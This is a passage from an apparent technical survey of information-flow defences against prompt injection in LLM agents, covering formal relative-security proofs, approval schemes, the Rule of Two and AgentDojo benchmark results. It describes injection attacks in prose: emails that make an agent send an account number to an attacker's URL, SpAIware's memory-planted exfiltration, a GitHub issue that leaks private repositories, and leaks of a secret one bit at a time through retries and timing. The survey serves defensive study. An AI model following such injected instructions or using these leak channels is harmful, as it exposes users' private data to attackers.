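k = ⌊α(n + 1)⌋

and set the threshold at the k-th lowest score. With 999 groups and α at 1 per cent, k is 10. If a passage from a new group is equally likely to take any place in the ranking, it scores below the threshold with a probability of at most 10/1,000, or 1 per cent.

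In tests on prompts from 2,103 groups of open-source projects, Sightline missed about 1 per cent of the real influences and removed 44 to 66 per cent of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model. Which influences counted as real was based on the judgements of three LLMs. On AgentDojo, with α at 5 per cent, Sightline removed half of the label creep from an agent running on Qwen3-8B. An integrity policy that used the remaining labels still blocked all 34 attack calls, but with so few calls, the true failure rate could be as high as about 8 per cent.

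The guarantee holds only on average, and it assumes that new calls resemble the ones used to set the threshold. In one test with a target of 5 per cent, Sightline missed about 10 per cent of the influences in the 20 per cent of cases where the model was most confident. Attackers also have an incentive to write text that doesn't resemble the earlier examples. Xu and colleagues replayed recorded attacks that were not designed to evade Sightline, and many defences that passed such tests later failed against adaptive attackers.

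It is therefore unsafe to remove a label from an existing answer on the basis of measured influence. An application could instead use Sightline to choose which documents to leave out and then generate a new answer without them, as Siddiqui and colleagues do. This is safe because a missed influence would affect only the quality of the new answer.

### User approval

A person can also endorse a value. In the payment example, the application could show the user the account number and the amount and ask whether to proceed. The user's approval makes the account number trusted for that payment only.

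The user's answer is informative only if the user can check what is on the screen. Someone who asked the agent to look up a friend's account number probably doesn't know it, and wouldn't notice if an attacker had replaced it. The user can check the amount more easily. Ordinary software should also write the question and state where each value came from, because if the model writes the question, an injection can supply a reassuring explanation.

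Frequent approval requests may also wear users down. Willison worries about this fatigue, and Jacob and colleagues mention it as a possible drawback of CaMeL's approval requests. Their own agents don't ask the user anything during a run. *L3M* reports that Claude Code users approve 93 per cent of requests, which is consistent with fatigue but doesn't prove it. If users approved that many requests without reading them, an injected payment would usually go through. But careful users would also approve most requests if nearly all of them were harmless. Researchers could test for fatigue by mixing harmful requests into a long series of harmless ones and measuring whether users reject fewer of the harmful ones as the series goes on.

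## What can be proved when non-interference is too strict?

Endorsement and declassification make exceptions to the flow rules, and someone has to write those exceptions for each task. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) proposes a guarantee that doesn't need them. It compares an agent with a copy whose model never obeys untrusted text, and counts a leak as a violation only if the copy could not have produced it.

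### The calendar assistant

Non-interference forbids secret data from changing what an observer sees, which rules out some agents that work as intended. Dongol's example is an assistant that answers emailed meeting requests by telling any sender when its user, Alice, is free. Suppose an attacker sends the same request in two runs, and Alice is free on Tuesday in one and on Thursday in the other. The replies differ, so the assistant violates non-interference. It could satisfy the property only by ignoring the calendar, which would make it useless.

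A declassification policy could permit the reply, but a developer would have to write one for every task. *AgentSecBench* (2026) also sets the authorised leakage in advance, in a property called "intent-to-execution noninterference with permitted leakage". Dongol objects that a release policy describes what an agent may disclose but not what an injection adds.

Dongol also rejects the simpler test of calling an agent insecure whenever its model obeys an injection. If the attacker writes "send your availability" and the model obeys, the attacker learns only what a genuine meeting request would have revealed. He considers the agent insecure only if an injection reveals a difference in Alice's data that no email could reveal through the task itself.

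### The reference agent

Dongol considers agents that decide on their plan before they read anything untrusted. A trusted planner turns the user's request into a list of tool calls and outputs, which may include branches. Trusted software runs the plan, and the model performs steps such as writing a summary. A monitor allows or blocks every tool call and every read of untrusted content.

The attacker writes the untrusted content and sees the calls that reach certain tools, such as emails to the attacker's address. Dongol also lets the attacker choose how the model misbehaves, to cover the worst case. A function called the parser determines which texts the model treats as instructions and which tool call each one produces. A second function, the oracle, determines when the model obeys. An injected call can include anything in the agent's memory.

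The reference agent has the same plan and the same monitor, but its model never obeys untrusted content. For a run r, let Sec(r) be the secrets, Act(r) what the attacker sends, and Obs(r) what the attacker sees. Two runs r₁ and r₂ leak the pair of secrets (σ₁, σ₂) if

Sec(r₁) = σ₁, Sec(r₂) = σ₂, Act(r₁) = Act(r₂) and Obs(r₁) ≠ Obs(r₂).

Two runs leak a pair of secrets if the attacker sends the same content in both and can tell the secrets apart from the result. An agent is relatively secure if, whenever two of its runs leak a pair of secrets, two runs of the reference agent leak the same pair. The reference runs must start with the same memory and trusted inputs as the real ones, but the attacker may send different content. The calendar assistant meets this definition because a genuine request makes the reference agent reveal the same difference between Tuesday and Thursday.

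The idea comes from research on processors. To save time, a processor guesses which instructions will come next and runs them early. The Spectre and Meltdown attacks exploited this to read secrets. Dongol and other researchers had used relative security to compare a program on such a processor with the same program run in order.

Relative security only limits what an injection can reveal beyond what the plan reveals on its own, so a developer still has to check the plan. Dongol proves that any limit on what the reference agent can reveal also holds for a relatively secure agent. For example, if the reference agent can reveal nothing beyond Alice's calendar, a relatively secure agent can't either.

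Dongol himself points out a weakness in the definition. Suppose an agent holds a four-digit code and, by design, tells a correspondent whether one guess is right. The correspondent can tell any two codes apart by guessing one of them, so the reference agent already leaks the difference between every pair. If an injection makes the real agent send the whole code, the agent therefore still counts as relatively secure, although someone limited to guessing might need thousands of emails to find the code. The example fails a stricter version, uniform relative security, which requires the reference agent's input to depend only on what the attacker actually sent, not on the secrets.

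### Four small cases

Dongol tests the definition on 25 small agents. In the Leaky Summariser, Alice asks for a summary of an email. The agent's plan is to look up her account number, read the email and show her the summary. The agent can also fetch web pages, although the plan doesn't include this. The email comes from an attacker and contains an instruction to fetch an address on the attacker's site with the account number at the end. If the model follows the instruction, the attacker's server receives a different request for each account number. The reference agent makes no outside call, whatever the email contains. It therefore has no matching leak, so the summariser is not relatively secure.

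The Fenced Summariser has the same plan, but its monitor withdraws the fetching tool as soon as the agent reads the email. Dongol calls this a fence. The model may still request the page, but the monitor blocks the request, so the attacker sees nothing. Alice gets her summary as before, because the plan never needed the tool.

An injection makes Meeting Reply, the calendar assistant, send Alice's calendar in response to an email that isn't a meeting request. Alice did not authorise this, but the agent is relatively secure because a real meeting request would have led to the same disclosure. This conclusion applies only to that injection.

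In Reset Code, the same assistant also has access to a private code from another task, and the email contains an instruction to include that code in the reply. No email can make the reference agent send the code, so sending it is a new leak and the assistant fails. The model follows the attacker's instructions in both Meeting Reply and Reset Code, but only the Reset Code injection gives the attacker information that the task never gives anyone.

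### Where the fence has to go

In three further cases, the plan itself raises the fence by calling a lock, which withdraws the email tool for the rest of the run. The cases differ in when the plan does this:

| Case | Order of steps | What an injected email can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Late Fence | read the email, read a secret, lock | the secret and anything already in memory |
| Middle Fence | read the email, lock, read a secret | anything already in memory |
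| Early Fence | lock, then read the email | nothing |

With the Late Fence, the model can still send email after reading both the injection and the secret. The Middle Fence can leak private data even though the secret arrives after the lock. The agent may have kept private data from an earlier session, and the model can send that data before the plan reaches the lock. The reference agent starts with the same memory but never sends it, so this counts as a leak. With the Early Fence, the model can no longer send anything when it reads the injection.

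Processors have a similar fence, but it can be placed just before the instruction that would leak, because that instruction is already in the program. An injection adds its own leaking call, which the model may make at any point after reading the injected text. The model's fence therefore has to take effect no later than the first untrusted read.

### The fence theorem

The fence theorem extends the result for the Fenced Summariser to every plan. Let R be the set of tools that the monitor withdraws at the first untrusted read. An agent with this fence is relatively secure if:

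- every injected instruction calls a tool in R;
- no trusted input gives the agent a tool in R back;
- each injection is a single tool call;
- the model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance, which doesn't depend on the secrets or on the monitor's responses.

Within these limits, the theorem holds for every injected text and every possible model response. It covers attackers who see the content and order of the agent's messages but not their timing.

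The proof compares the two agents step by step. They differ only when the real agent makes an injected call. The model can't make such a call until it has read untrusted text, and by then the monitor has withdrawn the tool. The monitor refuses the call silently, so the agent's memory doesn't change, and the reference agent waits during that step. Each run of the real agent therefore matches a reference run with the same secrets, the same inputs and the same visible messages, which is more than relative security requires. The same argument also proves the uniform version.

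Dongol wrote the definitions and proofs in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant comparable to Lean. Claude Code helped generate the proofs, and Isabelle checked them all. The theorem does not support defences that mark untrusted text, such as spotlighting, because the attacker may choose a parser that treats marked and unmarked text identically.

Two of Dongol's cases show why the agent must not get its tools back too soon. In the Stale Loop, an agent reads a confidential report every day, then an email. Reading the email withdraws the email tool, and reading the next day's report restores it. On the second day, the model still has the first email in its context, follows the instructions in it and sends out the new report. The Session Loop avoids this by clearing the model's context before restoring the tool. Because such a loop never ends, its proof must also assume that the model does not keep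 following injections forever without returning to the plan.

Clearing the context is not enough if the agent has a long-term memory. In SpAIware, an attack on ChatGPT reported in 2024, a web page made the assistant save an instruction, which was then loaded into every later conversation. Each answer displayed an image whose address carried the user's messages to the attacker. Dongol restores the guarantee by treating the memory as untrusted, so the agent loses the tools again when it loads the memory.

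The theorem also fails if an injection can do more than make a single call. In Poisoned Variable, the plan reads an email and sends the same text back to its author. The injection makes no call, but it overwrites the stored email with a secret, and the plan's reply then sends the secret to the attacker. The fence doesn't help, because the plan needs the email tool and the injection never uses it. Dongol proves that a fence works against longer injected programs if the agent discards whatever they write to memory and the fence covers reads as well as calls. Reads matter because an injected program could open one of two pages on the attacker's server depending on a secret, and the attacker could see which one.

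### Approving a tool or an exact call

A fence withdraws tools after the first untrusted read. User approval lets the agent use one of them later, but the result then depends on what the user approves.

In Tool Approval, an agent repeatedly reads an email, receives a reply that Alice has approved, and sends it. Her approval permits the next use of the email tool, whatever the message contains. An attacker sends an email asking for private data in the agent's memory. If the model follows this instruction after Alice has approved her reply but before the plan sends it, the data goes out under her approval. The injected call also uses up the approval, so the monitor blocks her reply.

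A limit of one email per run has the same flaw, because the injection can trigger that email before the plan sends its own. Dongol's Budget First case is safe only because the plan sends its one permitted email before reading anything untrusted.

In Call Approval, Alice approves the exact text of the reply. If an injection tries to send an email, the monitor allows it only if it matches that text exactly, so the attacker never receives any other message. Dongol proves relative security for every injection that calls the email tool, provided the model doesn't obey injections forever and the attacker can't see timing.

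An attacker who can see timing may learn a little more. Suppose the injection tells the model to send a private value s at once:

- If s differs from the approved reply, the monitor refuses the injected call, and the reply goes out at its planned time.
- If s is identical to the approved reply, the monitor allows the injected call. The same text goes out one step early, and the monitor refuses the planned copy.

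The attacker receives one message with the same text in both cases, but its timing reveals whether s matches that text. This is little information if s is a long password, but if s can only be "yes" or "no" and Alice has approved "yes", the timing reveals s completely. The reference agent always sends at the planned time, so this is a new leak.

*Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) describes how an application could enforce approval of exact calls. Each approval expires, works at most once, and covers only actions that match every argument the user approved. A longer-lasting approval can leave some arguments open, but only within stated bounds. Trusted software writes the approval screen, except for one area labelled as the agent's untrusted explanation. The design also limits how many requests an agent can make, so that it can't wear the user down by asking repeatedly. These measures would prevent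 the substitution in Tool Approval, although exact matching alone doesn't hide when a message is sent.

Refusals can also reveal secrets. In Dongol's Allow-List case, the monitor lets the agent fetch only a newsletter. An injection can tell the model to fetch the newsletter if a secret is 0 and a forbidden page otherwise. An attacker who sees whether the newsletter request went out then learns whether the secret is 0, even though the request contains nothing private. This leak falls outside the fence theorem's weaker attacker model, which only compares runs in which the same number of messages reach the attacker. The fence still prevents the leak because it blocks both requests.

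### The lethal trifecta

Developers had informal rules resembling a fence before Dongol's proof. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warned against giving one agent access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to send information out. An agent with all three can leak data when its model follows injected instructions. Willison argues that the only reliable protection is to remove one of the three, and that the ability to send information out is usually the easiest to remove. The Leaky Summariser has all three, and its fence removes that ability when untrusted content arrives.

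In the GitHub attack that Willison cites, a single set of tools supplied the whole combination. The agent could use them to read public issues, which anyone can file, read private repositories, and open pull requests (proposed changes) that the public can see. A stranger used an issue to tell the agent to publish private data in a pull request. Dongol models this attack and proves that withdrawing the pull-request tool at the first untrusted read would have stopped it. But the user had asked the agent to deal with the issues, which may have required a pull request.

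The trifecta covers only the theft of data. An agent that can read strangers' messages and delete files is dangerous even if it has no way to send data out.

### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) extends the trifecta to other harmful actions. It also draws on a rule for programmers of the Chromium browser, dating from 2019, which Willison's *Chromium Docs* (2025) quotes. That rule allows code to combine at most two of untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe programming language and high privilege. Under Meta's version, an agent may have at most two of these properties within a session:

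- A: it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three must start a new session with an empty context or work under supervision, such as human approval. Meta applies this to an email assistant much like the one in the Project X case. The developer can restrict it to emails from trusted senders, remove its access to sensitive data, or limit its sending to trusted recipients or to drafts a person has checked.

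Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, welcomed the rule because "changing state" covers attacks that steal nothing. But he objected that Meta's diagram marked the combination of untrusted input (A) and the power to change things (C) as safe, when the two can do harm without any private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that B includes every sensitive system as well as private data, so an agent without B can change only things that don't matter to its user's security. Meta nevertheless changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk". The reply answers the objection only if developers recognise every system that matters, and they could easily overlook a shared calendar or a public account in the user's name.

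Both rules count an agent's abilities, so they can't distinguish Meeting Reply from Reset Code. Each agent reads strangers' emails, has private data and sends replies. The Rule of Two would require supervision for both, even though Alice wants Meeting Reply to answer anyone who asks for a meeting.

The order of steps also matters. Meta lets an agent change its combination during a session, for example by browsing the web first and then switching communication off when it needs internal systems. The Middle Fence uses the same order, so Meta's approach is safe only if the agent holds nothing private while it browses. In Meta's example of a research agent, the developer limits private information "beyond the initial prompt". An injection could still make the agent send out anything private in that prompt.

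The rule can also allow leaks through restricted channels. Meta's example of a travel assistant satisfies the rule partly by opening only web addresses from trusted sources. As in the Allow-List case, an injection could make the assistant decide whether to open a permitted address based on a secret. An attacker who could observe those requests would learn something about the secret from each one.

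An application that enforces the Rule of Two also has to keep track of what an agent has read. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) makes the properties "sticky", so an agent that has read private data keeps property B until its session ends, even if the application withdraws the tool that supplied the data. Any sub-agents inherit the property, and the agent can't clear it by asking for a new session. The design approximates a record of information flow, but it can't follow data passed to an unrelated party.

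### Cases outside the theory

Relative security concerns leaks, so it does not cover hijacking in which the attacker learns nothing. An injected email could make an agent delete Alice's files or pay the wrong account, and the agent could still satisfy relative security. The Rule of Two addresses such actions more directly, although it offers no proof.

Dongol also excludes agents whose model chooses every call as it goes along, including the ordinary agent loop and the planner in FIDES. These agents have no plan fixed before the first untrusted read, so there is no reference agent to compare them with. The theory also excludes tools whose answer depends on the request, such as a search engine run by the attacker, because the attacker could read the query before choosing a reply.

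Relative security can't be checked one tool at a time. The Leaky Summariser is secure with only the inbox or only the fetching tool, but leaks with both. Removing a tool can also make a secure agent insecure. Suppose a plan emails a secret to the attacker by design, and an injection sends the same secret through a web address. While the email tool works, the injection reveals nothing extra. If the monitor withdraws that tool, the reference agent no longer reveals the secret, and the injected request becomes a new leak.

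Relative security also does not measure usefulness. The reference agent runs under the same monitor, so a fence that prevents the real agent from finishing its task also prevents the reference agent from finishing. A monitor that refuses every call trivially satisfies the definition, and Dongol says that developers must test separately whether the agent completes its tasks.

With a simple fence, the Project X assistant would fail such a test because the fence blocks the email to the manager, just as a single label for the whole context does. In another of Dongol's cases, each recipient has a separate sending tool, and the fence leaves only the tool for the recipient Alice chose available. The same arrangement would let the Project X summary through and stop the email to the outsider. The proof for that case doesn't cover injections that write to the permitted recipient, so it doesn't rule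 out extra messages to the manager.

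## How much security and usefulness do these agents show in tests?

Tests of flow control have to measure both how many attacks succeed and how many of the user's tasks the agent still completes. Most studies of flow control measure both with AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office tasks.

### How AgentDojo works

Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *AgentDojo*, built four simulated environments. Each has invented data, such as an inbox or a bank account, and tools that read and change the data. The researchers wrote a set of user tasks and a set of attacker goals for each environment, then paired every task with every goal:

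| Environment | Tools | User tasks | Attacker goals | Pairs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |

That gives 97 user tasks and 629 pairs. In banking, for example, a user might ask the agent to pay a bill described in a text file, while the attacker wants it to send as much money as possible to another account. A test of one pair has four steps:

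1. The software puts the attacker's text in a place that an outsider could plausibly control and that the agent will read during the task, such as the body of an email.
2. The agent works on the user's task, and its tool calls change the simulated data.
3. A short program written for that task compares the data before and after the run, reads the agent's answer, and decides whether the agent completed the task.
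4. Another program checks whether the agent carried out the attacker's goal.

Debenedetti and colleagues graded the agent with ordinary programs because an injection that works on the agent might also work on an LLM grading it. Their method doesn't test whether the agent would retrieve the malicious text, since the agent always finds it.

AgentDojo reports three scores:

- **Benign utility** is the share of user tasks the agent completes when there is no attack.
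- **Utility under attack** is the share of pairs in which the agent completes the user's task without harmful side effects.
- **Attack success rate** is the share of pairs in which the agent carries out the attacker's goal.

The standard attack is a note that tells the agent to do the attacker's task before the user's. Researchers can add other attacks, and Debenedetti and colleagues warned from the start that a fixed set would not be enough, because any particular attack is easy to stop with a weak defence. The US AI Safety Institute later extended the benchmark for a joint exercise with its British counterpart, according to Inspect Evals' *AgentDojo*.

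### What enforcement costs in completed tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES, the planner that hides untrusted results in variables, on all 97 user tasks. They compared it with a basic planner, which reads every tool result and keeps one label for the whole context. With GPT-4o, averaged over five runs, the planners completed these shares of the tasks when nobody attacked them:

| Planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
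|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no policy checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 84.3% |
| Basic, with policy checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% | 41.9% |
| FIDES, with policy checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 50.0% |

Costa and colleagues report that FIDES's task completion rate is 8 percentage points higher than the basic planner's under the same enforcement, with each environment given equal weight. If every task counts equally, the advantage is about 11 points. Either way, FIDES recovers only a small part of the performance lost to the checks, since the unprotected planner completed 84 per cent of tasks.

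FIDES did worse than the basic planner in the travel environment. The policies there let an agent use many of the tools even after it has read untrusted text, so hiding the text brought little benefit. GPT-4o also often mishandled the variables. Replacing it with OpenAI's o1, a model trained to reason before it answers, raised FIDES's travel score from 41 to 68 per cent. Across all environments, FIDES with o1 had a task completion rate 16 percentage points higher than the basic planner with checks.

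Some of the remaining failures are deliberate, such as refusing to follow instructions in an untrusted file. Others are mistakes by the model. In one Slack task, the planner requested a list of channels it didn't need, which lowered the integrity of its context and blocked the rest of the task.

A test can also count a task as completed when the agent acted on incomplete evidence. In one AgentDojo banking task, the user asks the agent to change the password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the transaction descriptions, so the planner had only trusted details such as amounts and dates. It judged a large payment suspicious and changed the password without reading what the payment was for. AgentDojo counted this as a success, and no policy forbade it.

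Garby and colleagues tested Randori, the agent they wrote in LLMbda, on the 16 banking tasks. They also reran CaMeL, whose privileged model writes a program before the agent reads any data, with its policy checks off and on. Each agent attempted every task three times:

| Agent | Model | Harmless runs completed | Successful injections |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 (75.0% ± 18.9) | 2 of 432 |
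| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 (64.6% ± 22.0) | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 (66.7% ± 23.4) | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 (70.8% ± 21.4) | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 (37.5% ± 26.6) | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 (37.5% ± 26.6) | 0 of 357 |

Randori's checks were always on. With a third model, Qwen3.7-plus, Randori resisted all 432 attacks, bringing its total to two successful injections in 1,296 attacked runs. CaMeL's totals are smaller because some of its attacked runs did not finish.

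Turning on the checks roughly halved the number of tasks CaMeL completed. Garby and colleagues say Randori avoids this loss mainly because its planner can endorse untrusted data when a task requires it. But endorsement can't be the whole explanation, because Randori with MiMo-v2.5 completed 26 runs without endorsement, eight more than CaMeL with checks. Randori also enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies, so the two agents worked under different rules. Garby and colleagues built Randori, and the CaMeL team had no chance to tune CaMeL for this comparison.

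### Sixteen tasks and wide intervals

The margins in the table are 95 per cent confidence intervals, and they are wide because the test has only 16 tasks. Repeating a task three times adds little information if the agent usually gets the same result each time. Garby and colleagues therefore averaged the three attempts at each task and calculated the margin from the 16 averages. If they had treated the 48 runs as independent, Randori's margin with GPT-5.2 would have been about 12 points instead of 19.

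Randori's lead over CaMeL with the checks off is 8 points with GPT-5.2, well within the error. Its lead over CaMeL with the checks on is 37.5 points. If we treat the two results as independent, the margin on that difference is

√(18.9² + 26.6²) ≈ 33 points.

Randori very likely completes more banking tasks than CaMeL with its checks on, but 16 tasks are too few to tell by how much. The real advantage could be anywhere from about 5 to 70 points, though the range would probably be narrower if the calculation accounted for both agents attempting the same tasks.

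Perfect security scores have a margin too. If an agent resists all of n different attacks, the lower end of the interval that Garby and colleagues use (a Wilson interval) is

n / (n + z²), with z = 1.96.

If an agent resists all 47 pairs of a task and an attack, the lower end of the confidence interval is 92.4 per cent. The agent would have to resist about 380 different pairs to raise that to 99 per cent, and repeating the same 47 would not be enough.

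### Which attacks reach the flow rules?

Planning before reading stops many of AgentDojo's attacks, whatever the agent's policies are. Garby and colleagues put 97 of the 144 banking pairs in this category. For example, an injected payment request fails when the user wants only a summary of recent transactions. In the other 47 pairs, the program the agent would normally write contains the calls the attacker needs, so only these pairs test the label checks. Both successful injections against Randori, the ones with the replaced bill, came from this group.

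Planning before reading untrusted text does not always stop an attack. In one banking task, the agent must read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With its policy checks off, CaMeL wrote a small interpreter, which reads each instruction in the file and calls the matching tool. The program was fixed before the agent read any untrusted text, but whoever wrote the file could still choose the tool calls. Two attacks succeeded this way, although Garby and colleagues had expected the architecture to stop them.

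Researchers also have to decide what counts as a successful attack. Costa and colleagues reviewed every success that AgentDojo recorded and discounted those they considered harmless or wrongly scored:

| Planner | Successes recorded by AgentDojo | Successes after review |
|---|---|---|
| Basic, no policy checks | 160 | 152 |
| FIDES, no policy checks | 23 | 21 |
| Basic, with policy checks | 20 | 0 |
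| FIDES, with policy checks | 3 | 0 |

The reviewers discounted a success recorded by AgentDojo if the monitor had blocked the call, if the injection changed only the text of an answer, or if the policy allowed the action. For example, the policy allowed a Slack message that contained no link and revealed nothing confidential, though a user might still object to an unwanted message sent in their name. The claim that FIDES stops every injection in the benchmark therefore means that it stops every one that breaks its policies. The table also shows that hiding untrusted text is not enough, since 21 injections succeeded when the planner could reveal the text and no policy check followed.

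CaMeL's developers also report two successful injections in their own evaluation, according to Garby and colleagues. In one, the agent made a payment as directed by a document, a case they place outside the attacks CaMeL is meant to stop. In the other, the agent only quoted a hostile hotel review, as in TACIT's one recorded failure. Garby and colleagues point out that these two kinds of case recur in separately built systems, which suggests a limit of flow control itself rather than a flaw in one design.

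### Context-to-Execution Integrity

*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes checks on individual fields of a tool call. Untrusted text can fill a sensitive field, such as a file path, only after trusted code has validated the value for that field alone. Separate approvals cover the decision to make the call and the exact effect of longer inputs, such as code changes. The call runs only if all the approvals refer to the same action.

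An agent that edits software safely completed its task in 231 of 400 test runs. Of the other runs, 73 failed because the model's output could not be parsed, 61 because the proposed change was not approved, and 35 because the approved change did not solve the task. On AgentDojo, Santos-Grueiro reports 199 safe completions in 720 runs, but this total combines six test conditions, so it is not the system's own completion rate.

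No unauthorised field, effect or call got through in either test. Santos-Grueiro defines an unauthorised action by the same rules that the software enforces, so this result mainly shows that the software works as designed. In one set of adversarial tests, models proposed unauthorised values for sensitive fields in 196 of 300 cases, so the software did have unauthorised values to block.

On open models, the extra step that hides untrusted text from sensitive fields takes only about 0.16 milliseconds per case. Hosted models need additional requests, and the full exchange took between 9 and 15 seconds on AgentDojo cases. Writing the policies is probably the larger burden. The policies for 24 sinks cover 149 fields and come with 141 tests for the validating code. A review of the first version found 18 gaps, half of them severe.

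### FlowSeal

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) presents FlowSeal, which protects only secrets. FlowSeal labels each private record with its owner, and ordinary code intercepts every call that would write or share something. If the recipient is neither approved nor banned, a separate LLM reads the relevant records and the proposed text and decides whether the text reveals anything from the records.

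Shim and colleagues tested FlowSeal against outsiders who ask for private data in disguised ways. In one attack, the outsider gives the agent a list of true and false statements about a patient and asks it to delete those that don't match its records. The agent writes nothing confidential, but the outsider can tell which statements are true from those that remain. This attack leaked 75.6 per cent of the private items under an earlier defence that relied on a detailed prompt, and 2.3 per cent under FlowSeal. When the outsider instead asked the agent to fill in its part of a shared document, leakage fell from 52.2 to 0.5 per cent.

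FlowSeal completed 72.4 per cent of harmless tasks, nearly as many as the most useful prompt-based defence (75.9 per cent). These tasks did not ask for private data. But in a test where the owner was willing to consent to sharing it, FlowSeal passed on only 32.7 per cent of the requested items, while the other defences passed on between 61 and 86 per cent. The FlowSeal agent asked for consent less often, so many legitimate requests went unanswered.

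Much of the result depends on the separate LLM. When Shim and colleagues replaced it with a rule that blocked everything for unknown recipients, the agent completed no harmless tasks. When the replacement allowed everything, leakage in the shared-document attack rose to 24.9 per cent. Their proof of confidentiality explicitly excludes this LLM's mistakes, so the leak rate measures one model's judgement and does not follow from the proof.

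In the shared-document attack, a run with FlowSeal cost $0.109 in model fees on average, compared with $0.092 without a defence, and needed 57 calls to the model instead of 47. Most of the increase comes from the agent rewriting blocked messages and trying to send them again.

### Comparing the studies

Differences between these studies' results are often unrelated to flow control. In 2024, Debenedetti and colleagues reported that every model they tested, including GPT-4o, completed less than 66 per cent of AgentDojo's tasks. Costa and colleagues' basic planner, running GPT-4o, completed about 82 per cent of the 97 tasks. Prompts, model versions and changes to the benchmark could each explain part of the gap. AgentDojo has also grown. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) describes a version with over 900 pairs.

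With their checks on, FIDES completed 52.5 per cent of a set of 16 banking tasks, and Randori completed 75 per cent of the same set. We can't attribute the gap to the design of the agents, because Randori used GPT-5.2, a much newer model than the GPT-4o that FIDES used. Their policies also differ, and a developer can raise an agent's completion rate by writing a more permissive policy.

AgentDojo does not supply labels, so Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if any attack in the benchmark uses it. The labels for FIDES therefore relied on complete knowledge of where attacks could appear, which no real developer has. This labelling also made some tasks harder than necessary, because it treated emails from colleagues as no more trusted than emails from strangers.

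FlowSeal's figures come from a different kind of test. Shim and colleagues exclude prompt injection from the attacks they consider, and they use an LLM to judge whether each private item leaked. They did not run FIDES for comparison. They describe FIDES as leaving enforcement to the LLM, although ordinary code performs its policy checks.

The most reliable comparisons are within a single study, between runs of the same agent and model with the policy checks on and off. With GPT-4o, the checks lowered the basic planner's average by about 42 points and FIDES's by about 11. With GPT-5.2, they lowered CaMeL's by about 29. An agent designed around the labels loses less when the checks are turned on, but FIDES starts from a lower level because its variables lowered GPT-4o's score by 24 points even without the checks.

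### What fixed attacks show about a proof

The FIDES and Randori attack figures come from fixed injections. Such results can be very misleading for defences that depend on recognising malicious text, as the adaptive-attack study showed. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, confirmed this with a cheaper attack that relies only on how often its injections succeed. A second LLM uses the earlier attempts to write a new one. With GPT-4o-mini as the agent's model, five defences had almost completely stopped the fixed attacks, but the revised attacks got past four of them. PIGuard, a detector that had stopped every fixed attack, let 28 per cent of the revised ones through. Some defences that restrict an agent's actions resisted the revised attacks much better. Attacks succeeded most often when the user left the choice of action to the retrieved text, which is also the kind of task that flow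 control handles worst.

A proof of non-interference covers every wording of an attack, so testing more wordings adds little. Researchers learn more by testing the proof's assumptions and checking whether the program follows the rules that the proof describes. A successful attack exposes a false assumption or a case the policy allows, but an attack may fail for reasons unrelated to the policy checks. CaMeL resisted 617 of 622 attacks with its policy checks off, so similar results with the checks on are weak evidence of how well the checks work. The worst-case evaluation of ELBA, in which the researchers made the model pursue the attacker's goal, is a much harder test of such checks.

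CaMeL also shows that a fixed set of attacks can miss flaws. With its policy checks on, it resisted all 588 attacks that ran to completion. But when Garby and colleagues read its interpreter's code, they found an error that none of those attacks had revealed. Inserting an untrusted value into fixed text makes the value trusted.

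## How can flow control fail or fall short?

The mistake in CaMeL's handling of fixed text broke the system's rules, and a developer could fix it in the interpreter. Flow control can also fail when its code works as intended. Information can escape through a channel the system doesn't track, a developer can give a source the wrong label, or an attacker can do harm without breaking any rule.

### Two leaks in CaMeL

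Garby and colleagues describe two further leaks in CaMeL. The first is an implicit flow through a branch that the program skips. In a simplified version of their example, an agent manages a customer's account. Its program starts with two public variables, `low` and `rich`, both set to true, and then takes three steps:

1. If the balance is above a threshold, set `low` to false.
2. If `low` is still true, set `rich` to false.
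3. If `rich` is still true, send an email.

CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that the program takes, which gives these results:

| Balance | `low` after step 1 | `rich` after step 2 | Email |
|---|---|---|---|
| Above the threshold | false, secret | true, public | sent |
| At or below the threshold | true, public | false, public | not sent |

The variable `rich` stays public in both cases, so CaMeL allows the email, whose arrival reveals that the balance is above the threshold. The no-high-upgrade rule prevents this leak by stopping the program at step 1 if the balance is high.

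An outsider would find this leak hard to exploit by email, because CaMeL's privileged model writes the program before it reads any outside text. But a harmless request could lead the model to write a program with the same structure by accident.

The second leak comes from the loop that runs CaMeL again after a failed attempt. This loop is ordinary Python code that runs outside the label-tracking interpreter. Each new attempt starts with clean labels, even though it depends on error messages from the previous one. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it.

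One bit would matter little, but the loop lets the bits add up. Suppose the secret is a four-digit code. The first attempt could test whether it is above 4,999, and each later attempt could halve the remaining range. Fourteen attempts would be enough to find the code, since 2¹⁴ = 16,384 exceeds the 10,000 possibilities. CaMeL's developers acknowledge the problem and censor the error messages, but Garby and colleagues object that this offers no formal guarantee.

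A developer can fix this by running the loop inside the tracked language, as Randori does. Capping the number of attempts is simpler but only a partial remedy. Three attempts can reveal at most three bits in this way, but the count resets with the user's next request.

### Timing, refusals and visible actions

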